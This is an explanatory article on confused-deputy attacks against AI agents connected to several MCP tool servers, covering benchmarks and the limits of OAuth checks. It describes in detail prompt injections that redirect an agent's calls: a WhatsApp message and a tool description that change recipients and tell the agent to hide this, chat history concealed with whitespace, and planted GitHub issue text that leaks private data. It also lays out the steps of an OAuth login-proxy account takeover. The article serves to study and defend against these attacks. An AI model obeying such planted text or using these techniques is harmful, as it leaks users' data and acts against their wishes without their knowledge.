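# The confused-deputy problem in AI agents with several tool servers, and how to detect cross-server hops in their logs

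## What a confused deputy is, and how an agent with several tool servers becomes one

In computer security, a confused deputy is a program that ends up using its authority for a party that lacks it. The name comes from Norm Hardy's *The Confused Deputy* (1988), which describes an accident on a commercial timesharing system about eleven years earlier. AI agents have revived the problem. An agent is a language model that can call other programs as well as write text, and many people connect one agent to several programs, such as a mailbox and a bank account. The agent acts on all of them with its user's permissions, so an email it reads can lead it to make a payment the user never asked for.

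### The compiler at Tymshare

Tymshare sold time on shared computers, and its operating system protected files much as Unix does. The system had a compiler in a directory named SYSX. Customers who ran the compiler could name a file to receive debugging output. Tymshare's staff wanted to know which language features customers used, so they changed the compiler to collect statistics and write them to a file called (SYSX)STAT. To allow this, they gave the compiler a "home files license", which let it write to files in its own directory.

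The company's billing records were in the same directory, in a file called (SYSX)BILL. One customer learned that name and gave it to the compiler as the destination for debugging output. The compiler asked the operating system to open the file. The operating system found that the compiler had its licence and opened the file, and the debugging output overwrote the billing records.

Hardy rejects the obvious repairs. The compiler cannot block output to other directories, because customers have good reasons to send it there. It cannot block all output to SYSX either, since someone with legitimate access to that directory might want to write there. Banning only the name (SYSX)BILL would leave the other sensitive files exposed, and someone would have to change the compiler whenever a new one appeared. The code that wrote the debugging output had been correct until the staff added the licence.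 To foresee the problem, they would have had to examine every situation in which the compiler wrote a file.

Hardy attributes the fault to the compiler having two sources of authority. Customers lent it their permissions when they ran it, and the licence gave it a further permission. It should have written statistics under the licence and debugging output under the customer's permissions. But a request to open a file contained only the file's name, so the compiler could not specify which authority it was using, and the operating system allowed the request if either was sufficient.

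This kind of authority is now called ambient. A program can use it by naming an object and an operation, without showing on whose behalf it acts. Unix and Windows largely work this way. A program runs with the permissions of the user who started it, and when it asks for a file by name, the system checks only those permissions.

Tymshare first added a system call that let the compiler "switch hats", or choose which of its two authorities to use for a given request. Under the customer's authority, the attempt to open the billing file would have failed. But some applications needed more than two authorities, and things other than files also needed protecting. Hardy argues instead for capabilities, which are references that both identify an object and carry permission to use it. The compiler would hold a capability for the statistics file, and the customer would give it another for the debugging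 output instead of a file name. Customers without access to the billing file would have no capability for it and could not pass one on, so the compiler would not need to check file names.

### A definition in four conditions

Gallo (2026), in *Proof-of-Continuity*, states the problem in a form that does not depend on compilers or files. A privilege is a pair (*o*, *r*) of an operation and a resource, such as (write, billing file), and every party has a set of privileges, written Priv. A confused deputy occurs when there are a user *U*, a deputy *D* and a privilege (*o*, *r*) such that:

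1. (*o*, *r*) ∉ Priv(*U*): the user lacks the privilege;
2. (*o*, *r*) ∈ Priv(*D*): the deputy holds it;
3. *U* sends a request to *D*;
4. as a consequence of that request, *D* executes (*o*, *r*).

The customer at Tymshare is *U* and the compiler is *D*. Taken literally, the conditions also cover harmless cases. Each time a customer ran the compiler, it wrote to the statistics file, which the customer presumably had no right to modify. Gallo adds two tests: whether the request designated the target, and whether the requester was entitled to bring the action about. Writing to the statistics file passes because the compiler's makers had chosen that file, so the write was part of the compiler's own routine work. A payment gateway also passes because the shopper was entitled to cause the payment, even though the gateway moves money through banking systems the shopper cannot operate. Writing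 to the billing file fails both tests because the customer chose the file and had no right to have anything written there.

With an AI agent, the *U* of the definition is usually someone other than the user. *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* (Surapani, Kakitapelli and colleagues, 2026) describes a user who asks an agent to summarise the invoices in an inbox, where one message contains text asking for a payment. Whoever wrote that message cannot pay from the user's account, but the agent can. The message reaches the agent when it reads the inbox. If the agent then pays because of what the message said, all four conditions hold, and *U* is the person who wrote the message. In the paper's version, the agent passes the matter to a second agent that handles finance, and the restriction to reading is lost on the way.

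The third condition is not an exact match, because the author sent the message to a person and the agent came across it as data. Surapani and colleagues list this as one of three differences from the operating-system case. The other two are that the agent chooses its actions probabilistically and depending on its prompt, whereas the compiler followed fixed rules, and that authority is spread over people, organisations, agents and outside services.

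Gallo's own treatment of agents instead keeps the agent's user as the origin of the request and counts only the privileges that the request selects. A user who asks for a summary of a document has authorised only (summarise, document), so deleting the document falls outside the request even if the user has permission to delete it. The same call is improper under both readings. The second is easier to apply when examining a log afterwards, because the log can include the user's request but will seldom record who planted a text. It still requires knowing what caused each call. Gallo leaves to future work how to distinguish an action that a request caused from one that the program began by itself.

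### Many servers and one context

Much of the current work on confused deputies among agents concerns the Model Context Protocol (MCP), an open standard for connecting AI applications to external tools and data. Anthropic introduced it in late 2024 (*TrustShiftProbe*, 2026). According to Anthropic's *Bringing MCP 2026-07-28 to Claude* (2026), by July 2026 developers were downloading MCP's software kits more than 400 million times a month, and the directory for the company's Claude assistant listed over 950 servers.

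MCP has three roles. The host is the application that runs the model, for example a desktop assistant or code editor. A server is a program that offers tools, such as reading files or querying a database, and it may run on the user's machine or belong to an outside company. The host creates clients, and each client connects it to exactly one server. Under the design principles in Model Context Protocol's *Architecture* (2026), the conversation history stays with the host, and a server should not be able to read all of it or "see into" other servers.

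A client sends a server a `tools/list` message to get a list of its tools. Each entry has the tool's name, a schema for its arguments and an ordinary-language description of what the tool does and when to use it. To use a tool, the client sends a `tools/call` message with the tool's name and arguments, and the server returns a result. In an example from Model Context Protocol's *Architecture overview*, a call to the tool `weather_current` for San Francisco returns a sentence giving the temperature, wind and humidity. The host combines the tools of all connected servers into a single registry for the model, although a host with very many servers can load descriptions as they become relevant.

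The separation between servers therefore ends at the model, because tool descriptions and results from every server enter one shared context, the text from which the model works out its next step. Krakauer and Schaad (2026), in *Where Does MCP Security End?*, point out that this text is in the same natural language as the agent's governing instructions, and that the model cannot reliably tell the two apart. *Trivial Trojans* (2025) gives an example with a weather server and a banking server. The weather server cannot query the banking server, but the text it returns can include an instruction for the agent to do so. The Model Context Protocol (2026) project concludes on its blog that risk is "a property of the session, not of any single server". For example, a tool that searches email is fairly harmless alone, but much riskier in a session with a tool that can post to the web.

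A prompt injection is text planted in content that a model reads, which the model then follows as an instruction. The term dates from 2022. In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, published by the UK's National Cyber Security Centre in December 2025, David C gives the example of a recruiter who uses a model to score CVs. One candidate hides a line in a CV telling the model to ignore its previous instructions and approve the candidate for interview. This is the indirect form of the attack, in which the attacker has no access to the system and only writes something that it will later process.

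The title's comparison is to SQL injection, an old database flaw in which an attacker types a database command into a field meant for data, such as a name on a web form, and the database executes it. Programmers can prevent this by passing the data separately, as a parameter that the database will never treat as a command. David C argues that a language model has no place for such a barrier, because it only predicts the next token, or fragment of text, from all the text so far. A classical confused deputy can be repaired, but in this view a language model is an "inherently confusable deputy", and the people who build with it should concentrate on limiting the damage.

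Krakauer and Schaad similarly argue that Hardy's remedy, scoped authorisation, was a deterministic fix for a deterministic system, and that nothing equivalent exists for a model that may respond differently to the same input. Their point about the model is sound, but it does not settle what authority the model should have. Surapani and colleagues note that a strict capability discipline would remove ambient authority altogether, so a component with no reference to the bank account could not pay from it, whatever it had read. None of the frameworks they reviewed enforces this from end to end, and how to combine it with tasks stated in natural language is unexplored. They find that systems often approve a broad tool or a whole account before the work begins. Within that approval, the agent only has to name a tool and fill in the arguments, which puts it in much the same position as the compiler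 with its licence.

### Other meanings of the term

"Confused deputy" has at least two other meanings in writing about agents. Siu, He and colleagues (2026), in *A Framework for Formalizing LLM Agent Security*, use the term for an agent that lends its privileges to a user who lacks them. In their example, an employee asks a company's agent for everyone's salary. The employee has no access to the personnel database, but the agent has access for administrative work, and it answers. This is closer to the Tymshare case than an attack through planted text is, and the paper treats indirect prompt injection as a separate attack. *Risks and Controls for Multi-Agent Systems* (2026) defines a confused deputy as an agent that acts on a request nobody authorised.

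The Model Context Protocol's own *Security Best Practices* uses "confused deputy" for a login flaw in which an attacker exploits a server that relays access to an outside service and gets in without the user's proper consent. The threat taxonomy *MCP-38* (2026) uses the term the same way.

From here on, "confused deputy" means an agent steered by content it has read. This case needs a different defence from the salary query. A check on the employee's own permissions would stop that query, but it would not stop the agent from paying the planted invoice, because the agent's user is allowed to make payments from that account.

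### Cross-server hops

A cross-server hop is a call to one server made after the agent has taken in content from a different server. A run contains such a hop when planted text from one server leads to a call on another. The hop is data-carrying if the call's arguments contain a value that came from the other server. It is steered if content from another server caused the call and the call falls outside what the user asked for.

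None of these is a standard term. *MCPHunt* (2026), a framework for testing agents with several servers, uses "cross-boundary data propagation", and *Trivial Trojans* has "cross-tool exfiltration" in its subtitle. Other work uses "cross-server shadowing" or "lateral movement". These names overlap only partly. Exfiltration, for example, covers stolen data but not an unwanted payment or deletion. In Gallo's paper, a "hop" is any step of execution, whether or not it crosses between servers.

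Tool descriptions are also content, so in a host that loads all of them at the start, every call would strictly count as a hop. The examples below therefore count only tool results as content from another server, though a description can still influence any call in the run.

| | The user asked for the call | The user did not ask for the call |
|---|---|---|
| **Hop** | "Put the dates from Anna's email in my calendar." The agent reads the email, then calls the calendar server. | "Summarise my invoices." A message in the inbox asks for a payment, and the agent calls the bank's server. |
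| **No hop** | "What is in my calendar tomorrow?" The agent calls the calendar server and answers. | "Summarise my inbox." A message asks for copies of other mail, and the agent forwards them through the same mail server. |

Most hops, like the one in the calendar request, are almost certainly legitimate, because people often want agents to move information between systems. *MCP-Atlas* (2026) is a benchmark of how well models use real MCP servers. In it, 98.6% of tasks require tools from at least two servers, with a mean of 2.55 servers per task. The benchmark was designed to require multi-server work, so the figure does not measure everyday use. The tasks in *MCPHunt*, however, follow familiar office routines, such as writing a report from data and moving a project from one host to another. A detector that flagged every hop would flag nearly every *MCP-Atlas* task, even though the benchmark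 includes no attacker.

The forwarded mail shows the opposite error. A search for hops would miss that attack because it stays within the mail server. An unrequested hop also need not involve an attacker. Siu and colleagues describe a cooking assistant that is asked only for recipes but, after searching a recipe database, also looks through the user's medical records for dietary restrictions. If the two databases are on different servers, the agent has made a hop that the user didn't request and that no text in the recipes told it to make.

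## How text from one server leads an agent to call another

An agent works in rounds, and the host adds each tool result to the shared context before the model chooses its next step. Zhang, Li and colleagues (2025), in *MCP Security Bench (MSB)*, write the model's part in one round as

LLM(*p* ⊕ *T*, *q*, *O*)

Here *p* is the system prompt, the standing instructions that come before the conversation. *T* is the list of tool names and descriptions, which the client joins to the system prompt (⊕ means joining two strings). *q* is the user's request, and *O* is the series of observations so far, including every tool result. The user writes only *q*. The servers supply *T* and the tool results in *O*, so anyone who can write into either can change the next call without changing the user's request.

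### Text in a tool result

*WhatsApp MCP Exploited*, published by the security company Invariant Labs in April 2025, demonstrates two attacks on an agent that reads and sends WhatsApp messages through an MCP server. In one of them, the attacker only has to send an ordinary message to the target's phone number. When the agent next lists the target's chats, the server returns that message along with everything else in the inbox.

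The message contained instructions for any later use of the server's sending tool. The agent was to replace the recipient with a number the attacker had chosen and add the phone numbers of the user's recent contacts. The message described these changes as technically necessary for sending to work. Invariant Labs began it with characters that imitated the end of a message record in the server's output, so that the rest would seem to lie outside the record. In a test with the code editor Cursor, the attack extracted the user's contacts. Both the listing and the sending went through the WhatsApp server, so the run contained no cross-server hop.

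Invariant Labs published its next demonstration, *GitHub MCP Exploited* (2025), in May. GitHub hosts software projects in repositories, and anyone can open an issue, such as a bug report, on a public one. A user asked Claude 4 Opus, running in Claude Desktop, to review and address the issues in a public repository for a Pac-Man game. After reading planted text in one issue, the agent copied information from the user's private repositories into a pull request, a proposed change to the code, on the public project. Anyone could then read the names of private projects and the user's salary and plan to move to South America.

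Here too, one server handled every call, so the run contained no hop. The data moved between repositories that the agent had permission to use. The repository names in the call arguments would still show the move from public to private. If the private data had been on a separate file server, the same planted text would have produced a steered hop.

Claude Desktop asks the user to confirm each tool call by default. Invariant Labs notes that many users choose "Always Allow" instead and stop watching what the agent does.

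Neither attack needed a dishonest server. *Unsafe by Flow* (Hou, Zhao and Wang, 2026) studies how honest servers pass on outside content, assuming that the makers of the host, client and server all mean well. Its main example is a tool that fetches web pages. The agent supplies an address, and the server downloads the page, shortens it if necessary and puts the text in the result, so whoever wrote the page has written part of the model's context. Files, documentation, program output and code repository history can reach the model in the same way. In one published vulnerability, log text from a server for Kubernetes, a system for running software in containers, could influence a later tool call.

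Hou and colleagues built an analyser that traces a tool's return value backwards through the code to see whether it depends on outside content, and traces a call's arguments forwards to sensitive operations. They ran it on 15,452 repositories of MCP servers, and their manual review confirmed 118 vulnerable paths in 87 servers. Of these paths, 111 allow an attacker to execute code, so 87 is not a count of servers that can steer an agent. Passing on outside text is often not a programming error, since a tool for reading web pages, for example, has to return what is on them.

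*No-Box Vulnerability Analysis* (Zhang, Hu and colleagues, 2026) gives a better indication of how common the exposure is. It examined 177 tools on 20 widely used MCP servers. Human evaluators confirmed that 95 were open to indirect prompt injection, and 132 passed external data to the model without sanitising it. The study counts a tool as vulnerable if attacker-controlled text can reach the model in a form that could carry instructions, whether or not any particular model follows them. The figure of 95 is therefore a count of tools that offer an opportunity for attack, and it doesn't show how often attacks would succeed.

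### Text in a tool description

In the other WhatsApp demonstration, the agent had access to the same trusted server and to a second server controlled by the attacker. The second server offered a tool that returned a random fact of the day. The tool's description contained an instruction about the WhatsApp server's sending tool, much like the one in the incoming message. The agent was to send messages to the attacker's number, falsely described as a proxy that would forward them, and to include the results of any earlier chat listing. The description also contained a warning that the system would crash if the agent did otherwise, and an instruction not to tell the user.

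When the user then asked the agent to message someone, it called the WhatsApp tool with the attacker's number and the chat history. The agent never called the fact tool, and the two servers never communicated. Running the attacker's server in a sandbox, an environment that limits what a program can reach, would not have helped, because the attack used only the server's description, not its code. Writers on MCP use the term "shadowing" for attacks in which one tool's description changes how an agent uses another tool.

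A tool description has some advantages for an attacker over a tool result. If the host loads all descriptions at the start, the description is in the context before the user asks for anything and can affect every later request. A result enters the context only after the agent calls the tool that returns it. Invariant Labs found the incoming message slightly harder to exploit than the description. It suggested that this may be because some models are trained to give lower priority to instructions in tool results, and because results are less prominent in the context.

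An attack's wording has to suit the channel. The text that worked as a tool description failed as an incoming message until Invariant Labs adapted it. *MCPTox* (2025), a benchmark of attacks through tool descriptions, found that attack texts written for tool results succeeded far less often when moved into descriptions.

Cursor asked the user to confirm the WhatsApp tool call, but its dialog was misleading. It showed the recipient only as a phone number, which people who rely on their contact list may not recognise. The message field seemed to contain only a short greeting because a long run of spaces pushed the chat history out of view. The user had to scroll right to see it, and the interface hid the scroll bar. The user had also just asked the agent to send a message, so a request to approve one would have caused little suspicion.

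Hosts cannot avoid the problem by having the model ignore tool descriptions, because it needs them to use the tools. Descriptions influence the arguments a model passes even when nobody is attacking. In *MCP-SafetyBench*, Zong, Shen and colleagues (2025) added alarming warnings to the descriptions of harmless tools for managing code repositories. All four models tested kept using the tools, but GPT-5 and Grok-4 began making new repositories private, while GPT-4.1 and Qwen3-235B kept the default settings. The warnings had changed an argument that the user had not mentioned, in this case probably for the better.

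### Descriptions that change after approval

In the WhatsApp demonstration, the attacker's server first gave its fact tool a harmless description, which the user approved, then switched to the planted description at its second launch. Some clients show users a tool's description when they first connect a server, but according to Invariant Labs, these clients did not notify users of later changes. The old approval therefore covered a description the user had never seen. This is usually called a rug pull. An attacker can limit the change to a short period or a particular group of users, which makes it difficult to trace afterwards.

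*TrustShiftProbe* cites two real cases from 2025 in which a tool changed after it had gained trust. The package postmark-mcp had a clean record over fifteen versions before an update made it send the message data it processed to an unauthorised address. Because of a flaw named MCPoison, coding agents continued to trust a tool configuration after someone had changed the program behind it. Neither case depended on a model following planted text. The postmark server leaked the data itself, so the agent's log would have contained only the intended calls.

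Requesting a server's tool descriptions twice can reveal changes. *Exposed by Design* (2026), a security assessment of MCP servers on the public internet, uses a program that saves a server's tool list and requests it again after 30 seconds or after calling a tool. This can catch a server that changes its list within a session, but it would miss one that changes it only at its next launch, as the server in the WhatsApp demonstration did.

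### Added calls and altered arguments

Planted text can make an agent add tool calls, or change the arguments of a call that the user's request required. In the GitHub case, the agent made extra calls to read private repositories unrelated to the request. In the WhatsApp attacks, the agent sent a message as the user asked, but with a different recipient and extra content.

Zong and colleagues give a simpler example of an altered argument. A user asks about holdings in JNJ, the stock symbol for Johnson & Johnson. Text in a tool's description replaces the symbol with TSLA, the symbol for Tesla. The agent plans the task correctly and calls the expected tool, but requests data on the wrong company.

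An added call leaves an extra entry in the execution log, with its own tool name and arguments, and a reviewer who knows what the user asked for can question it. An altered argument adds no entry, so the log of the WhatsApp attack would contain a chat listing and a sent message, as it might in normal use. To notice the problem, a reviewer would have to know the intended recipient's number and see the whole message, including the part after the spaces.

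The attack through the fact tool's description is harder still to explain from a log. The attacker's server returned no results, so a log of calls and results would contain nothing from it. The run would also contain no hop under the counting rule adopted earlier, which leaves out descriptions. The log would show the cause only if it also included the descriptions the model received.

Some attacks combine the two effects. In the GitHub case, the user had asked the agent to address the issues, which could reasonably involve opening a pull request. Reading the private repositories was an added step, but the pull request may have been a legitimate call with the wrong content.

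An attacker who controls a tool can also define a parameter that the tool does not need. In one test in *MCP Security Bench*, the extra parameter is for the name of the language model, and the agent fills it in while doing what the user wanted. The call goes to the expected tool and server and matches the tool's published schema. If the extra value came from another server, the call would be a data-carrying hop. But an unexpected value does not prove an attack, because agents sometimes spread credentials between servers with no attacker present.

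The same benchmark includes a tool that returns a false error message with an instruction the agent supposedly has to follow to get its result. Another tool returns a message that it is no longer available and names a replacement, which carries out the attack. In a log, the added calls would look like routine recovery from a failure.

### How often steering succeeds

Researchers usually report an attack success rate, the share of attacked runs in which the agent carries out the attacker's goal. *MCPTox* provided an early large set of figures for MCP in August 2025, with the highest rate, 72.8%, for OpenAI's o1-mini. Its published version covers 20 agents and has 1,348 test cases built on 45 real servers and 353 tools. According to Inspect Evals' *MCPTox*, each case gives the agent a harmless request and a server with one poisoned tool, and another model judges whether the attack worked. The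 models are now old, and the test measures whether one tool can steer the agent to another, whether or not the tools belong to different servers.

*MCP Security Bench* has 2,000 attack instances built from 65 user tasks and 405 attack tools. The agents also had a file server and a desktop-control server, and the attacker's goals included ending a process and changing stored data. The researchers judged whether each attack had worked by inspecting the state of the workspace afterwards. The mean success rate across ten models and twelve attack types was 40.35%. The table gives results in per cent for five of the models and four of the attack types.

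| Model | Instruction in a description | Result posing as a message from the user | Poisoned data returned by an honest tool | Unneeded parameter |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5 | 48.9 | 0.3 | 30.0 | 98.8 |
| Claude 4 Sonnet | 66.9 | 46.9 | 40.0 | 93.8 |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash | 52.5 | 7.5 | 0.0 | 36.3 |
| DeepSeek-V3.1 | 18.4 | 65.6 | 75.0 | 92.5 |
| GPT-4o-mini | 2.6 | 91.8 | 40.0 | 95.0 |
| Mean of all ten models | 20.2 | 45.7 | 20.0 | 76.5 |

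On average, instructions in tool descriptions and poisoned data from honest tools succeeded about equally often, but results varied widely between models. GPT-5 almost never obeyed a result that posed as the user, but it followed nearly half of the instructions in descriptions. GPT-4o-mini did the opposite. Adding an unneeded parameter was the most successful attack, perhaps because filling in parameters is a normal part of using a tool and the agent has no separate instruction to resist.

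*MCP-SafetyBench* covers 245 cases and 13 models on real MCP servers. Overall success ranged from 29.8% for Qwen3-235B to 48.2% for o4-mini. These totals include attacks in which the experimenters tampered with the host itself, such as forging identity data, which succeeded every time. The categories closest to steering by text gave the following ranges across the models:

- 19% to 52% for shadowing
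- 29% to 57% for instructions in a tool's result
- 45% to 91% for descriptions that redirected the agent to another tool
- 0% to 28% for descriptions that altered a parameter

The samples are small. The percentages for redirection, for example, are all multiples of one eleventh, which suggests about 11 cases per model.

Zong and colleagues also varied the number of servers. With GPT-4.1 on financial tasks, attacks succeeded in 43.4% of cases with two servers, 45.3% with three and 47.2% with four. They conclude that more servers increase the risk. But there were only 53 financial cases, so each increase is one more successful attack, which is too few to establish a trend.

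*Evaluating and Improving the Robustness of Large Language Models* (2026) makes a more direct comparison. In its benchmark of 847 scenarios, attacks that spread across servers succeeded 61.3% of the time with MCP and 19.7% with other ways of connecting tools. This gap was the largest for any attack type in the comparison. The models were Claude 3.5 Sonnet, GPT-4o and Llama 3.1 70B, all from 2024, so the percentages are a poor guide to current agents.

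*TrustShiftProbe*, from August 2026, connects an agent to one server that returns accurate results for several calls and then manipulated ones. In most of its nine attack types, the attacker wins if the agent's final answer contains the server's false information or if withheld data spoils the task. These attacks can succeed without an improper call, so the paper's 69.5% mean is not a rate of steering. The attack meant to make the agent seek secrets outside the task succeeded between 5% and 11% of the time for each of the six models. Success at gradually collecting data across several tools ranged from 0% for GPT-5 to 54.8% for Claude Opus 4.8. These last two attacks are closer to steering, but they still involve only one server.

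Tests from autumn 2026 found much lower success rates for some attacks on newer models. *On Task, Off Track* (2026) tested GPT-5.6 Sol, Gemini 3.7 Flash, Claude Opus 5 and three other recent models on AgentDojo, an established set of tasks for agents with tools. When the attacker had a fixed goal, the first attempt succeeded in 0% to 2.2% of cases. When the goal was a wrong outcome close to the user's own task, the first attempt succeeded in 3.4% to 16.4% of cases. With three attempts, the range was 7.5% to 32.4%.

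Attacks with an obviously foreign goal can therefore succeed rarely even when attacks that subtly change the user's task succeed much more often. This matters for log review because a call changed in this way may differ from the user's request only in an argument. In the older figures from *MCP-SafetyBench*, however, altered parameters succeeded less often than redirected calls. The two tests used different channels and models, so neither settles which form of steering is easier in general.

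*Who Is Prompt-Injecting Coding Agents?* (2026) tested five recent models in November on 43 real attacks found hidden on GitHub. GPT-5.6 Luna, the smallest and fastest, complied with eight (19%). GPT-5.6 Terra and the Haiku, Sonnet and Opus versions of Claude 5.5 complied with none. Small, fast models suit agents that run on every new issue, so the most susceptible model in the test was also the kind most likely to encounter such attacks.

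The models sometimes resisted the injection but failed to complete the user's task. Claude Opus 5.5 returned no answer in 22 of the 43 runs and Sonnet 5.5 in 16. Some of these refusals persisted after the researchers removed the hidden text, apparently because of the visible content. In 24 runs, Sonnet completed the legitimate task and pointed out the injection, which is much more useful than returning no answer.

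The results also weaken the earlier conclusion in *MCP Security Bench* that more capable models are more vulnerable because they are better at using tools and following instructions. In the GitHub test, only the smallest model complied. Greater capability can help an agent carry out an attack, but training can evidently make it less likely to start one.

The measured rate of compromise also depends on the scoring method. *INFUSE* (2026), a benchmark of indirect prompt injection with 19 models, scored the same runs in two ways. A judging model classed 19.6% of them as compromised, while a rule-based check classed 15.4% as compromised.

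A scoring rule can also mistake authorised work for an attack. Ahmed and Abbas (2026), in *Labels Are Not Endpoints*, audited their own experiment on poisoned tool descriptions, which had appeared to show a clear effect. Their program counted a run as a successful attack if the description was poisoned and the agent had used at least two tools, even when the user's task required both. The same behaviour under a clean description could never count as an attack. When they stopped the label from depending on whether the description was poisoned, and counted exact repetitions of a request only once, 58 requests that the program had recorded as attacks or attempted attacks turned out to be authorised work.

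The experiment was also much smaller than it seemed. Only 180 of its 10,200 runs were different requests, made by testing 15 tasks with three versions of the descriptions on four small models. The rest were exact repetitions with the same output. Three confirmed transfers of protected data and one case of unauthorised forwarding remained after the correction.

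## Why the receiving server cannot tell who asked

In the earlier invoice example, the user only wants a summary, but the agent reads a planted payment request through a mail server and then calls the bank's server to pay. The bank's server could refuse, but it would first need a way to distinguish this call from a payment the user wanted.

### What the server can check

MCP's authorization rules use OAuth, a standard that lets people give a program access to an account without giving it their password. The user signs in at an authorization server and approves the access. The authorization server returns a code, which the program exchanges for an access token. The program then includes the token in every request to the service. Under the official specification of the Model Context Protocol, the receiving server can check:

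- whether the token is genuine and has not expired
- whether the token's audience, the server it was issued for, is this server
- whether the token's scopes, the permissions attached to it, cover the operation

If the user has allowed the agent to make payments, the planted payment passes all three checks. The call also contains the tool's name and arguments, such as the payee and the amount. It does not contain the user's request or the email, because MCP keeps the conversation with the host. If the user had asked for the same payment, the bank's server could have received an identical call.

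Narrow scopes give some protection. A token that only covers reading balances cannot make a payment, so the server would reject the call and name the missing scope. However, the specification recommends that a client acting for a user then request a new token that adds the missing scope to those it already has. A permission granted for one task can therefore still be available when planted text arrives during another. If a server gives no guidance on which scopes an operation needs, the client requests every scope the server lists.

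Some calls carry no token. Authorization is optional in MCP, and a local server that communicates with the host through standard input and output should take its credentials from its environment instead.

Under the revision of 28 July 2026, a tool can also respond to a call by requesting more input from the user, such as a confirmation, and the client then repeats the call with the answer. In the release announcement (Model Context Protocol, 2026), the database company Supabase gives the example of confirming a query that would delete data. But the answer comes back through the client, so the server relies on the host to show the question to a person.

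### The login-proxy attack

The attack that MCP's security guidance calls the confused-deputy problem happens during login, before any tool call. It involves an MCP server that acts as a proxy for another company's service. The proxy uses one fixed client ID with that company's authorization server, but it lets any number of MCP clients register with the proxy itself. The attack described in the Model Context Protocol's guidance works as follows:

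1. A user logs in through the proxy and approves its access to the outside service. The outside authorization server stores a cookie in the user's browser, recording consent for the proxy's client ID.
2. An attacker registers a new client with the proxy and gives an address under the attacker's control as the place to send login codes.
3. The attacker sends the user a link that starts a login for the new client.
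4. The user clicks the link. The outside authorization server finds the cookie, skips the consent screen and sends a code to the proxy.
5. The proxy creates its own code and sends it to the attacker's address.
6. The attacker exchanges that code for a token and can now use the outside service through the proxy as if they were the user.

The proxy is the deputy. The user approved its access to the outside service, and it used that access for a client the user had never approved.

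Obsidian Security's *When MCP Meets OAuth* describes the same arrangement, in which two logins share one client ID. According to AuthZed, an authorization company, Obsidian demonstrated one-click account takeover using the MCP server of Wix, a website builder, and found a way to bypass consent on the server of Square, a payment company.

MCP requires the proxy to record which clients each user has approved and to check that record before starting the outside login. The proxy's consent page must name the client, the permissions requested and the address that will receive the code. This address must exactly match the one the client registered. With these checks, the attacker's link would show the user a request to approve an unfamiliar client.

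They would not stop the planted payment, because the user has already approved the agent's client and the person who wrote the email does not need a client or token of their own.

### Tokens used at the wrong server

Token passthrough occurs when an MCP server accepts a token without checking that it was issued for that server, then forwards it to another service. Someone with a stolen token could use such a server to reach the other service. That service's logs may show the requests as coming from the wrong program, which makes an incident harder to investigate.

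MCP requires audience binding, which ties each token to the server it was issued for, through an OAuth extension called RFC 8707. When a client requests authorization and a token, it must include the address of the MCP server where it will use the token. The receiving server must reject a token issued for a different server. If it needs to call another service, it must obtain a separate token for that service.

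den.dev's *Update To MCP Authorization Spec* explains the rule with a phishing example, in which someone searches the web for a server to manage travel plans and finds a convincing page. Without audience binding, a fake server that received a token for the real travel service could use it there. With audience binding, a token issued for the fake server would not work at the real one. The protection requires an authorization server that supports the extension, although MCP clients must send the address either way. The rule predates the 2026 revision, because Model Context Protocol (2025) already included it in June 2025.

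In the invoice example, the mail server and the bank's server each receive only the token issued for that server. Only text passes between them, through the model's context, and audience binding does not restrict text.

### What changed in July 2026

The July revision closed several more gaps in the login process. The table shows why each change leaves the planted payment unaffected.

| Change | Failure it addresses | Why the planted payment still passes |
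|---|---|---|
| The client checks which authorization server issued a login response | An attacker who runs one authorization server tricks the client into sending it a code from an honest one | The client obtained its token from the bank's own authorization server |
| The client keeps separate credentials for each authorization server | A client reuses credentials from one authorization server at another | The client used the correct credentials |
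| Clients identify themselves through a document on the web, and the older method of self-registration is deprecated | A program claims to belong to a web domain that it does not control | The call comes from the user's real application |

The issuer check works only if the honest authorization server includes its identifier in the response, which the specification recommends but does not yet require. The identity document proves who controls a web domain, but not which program is listening on the user's own computer.

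The revision also removed sessions from the protocol, so a server that needs to connect several calls, for example to maintain a shopping cart, gives the model an identifier to pass back as an argument. The server should tie the identifier to the authenticated user so that nobody else can use it. A steered call would still pass this check, because it comes from that user's agent.

Another change puts the tool's name in a request header. A gateway, which is a program between the agent and its servers, can use that name to permit or refuse calls. A rule based on the header could block all payments, but the header does not identify the payee. The revision also deprecates MCP's own logging feature.

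*MCP's Auth Hardening*, by the security company Tigera, rightly argues that the changes improve how a client authenticates to a server but leave authorization of individual requests outside the specification. Each change helps establish which program is calling and whether its credentials are valid, but in a steered hop the expected program is calling with valid credentials.

### How often the checks are missing

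Many servers do not make even the checks described above. In *Give Them an Inch and They Will Take a Mile*, Huang, Dai and colleagues (2026) examined 6,137 MCP servers written in Python, JavaScript or TypeScript. Their program traced the code from each incoming tool call to sensitive operations, such as running a command or reading a file, and looked for an authorization check along the way. Where the code was unclear, the program started the server and called the tool to see whether the call succeeded.

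The study reports that 2,846 servers (46.4%) were insecure. However, its breakdown by category adds up to 3,160 insecure servers out of 5,714 (55%), so the figures support only a rough estimate of half. In the breakdown, 1,279 servers had no authorization check, 242 checked once and then reused the result, and 1,639 checked while running but relied on stored state or checked inconsistently.

Some servers, including ones for Slack and Amazon's cloud services, logged in with powerful credentials at startup and used them for every caller. Anyone who could reach such a server could use the account without its credentials. In a separate analysis of 87 popular MCP projects, Huang and colleagues found eight with authentication problems that could let an attacker run commands remotely.

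The survey probably overstates the immediate danger for servers designed to run locally for one person. Under MCP, these servers are not expected to check tokens, and an attacker would first need a way to reach them. The flaw also differs from steering. Even a server that could tell its callers apart perfectly would accept the planted payment, because the caller is the user's own agent.

### Access to a tool as permission to act

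The program that runs the agent could check a call before sending it. *Capability Gates Are Not Authorization* (Mellafe Zuvic, 2026) audited the public code of three widely used agent toolkits: LangChain with LangGraph, LlamaIndex and the Stripe Agent Toolkit. It looked for a fixed check on the values in each call that would run before the call took effect and refuse it if anything went wrong.

All three let developers choose which tools an agent can use, but none checked argument values against an authorization policy by default. They could reject an argument of the wrong type, such as text in place of a number, but not a correctly formatted account number for an account that should not receive the money. Developers can add their own checks, so the finding applies only to the defaults.

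To demonstrate the gap, Mellafe Zuvic gave LangChain a prepared model output containing a call to change a merchant's payout account to the attacker's. LangChain executed the call on a simulated payment system. ScopeGate, a program written for the study, blocked the same call because the account was not on the operator's list. ScopeGate also limits payment amounts and refuses any tool that its policy does not cover.

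ScopeGate blocked all 48 prepared attempts to bypass it. It also blocked all 29 unauthorized calls from a model that received the reason for each refusal and tried again. In a separate test, it allowed all ten legitimate calls. The prepared attempts had exposed an error in an earlier version, which accepted a payment whose amount was "not a number", a special value computers use for undefined results.

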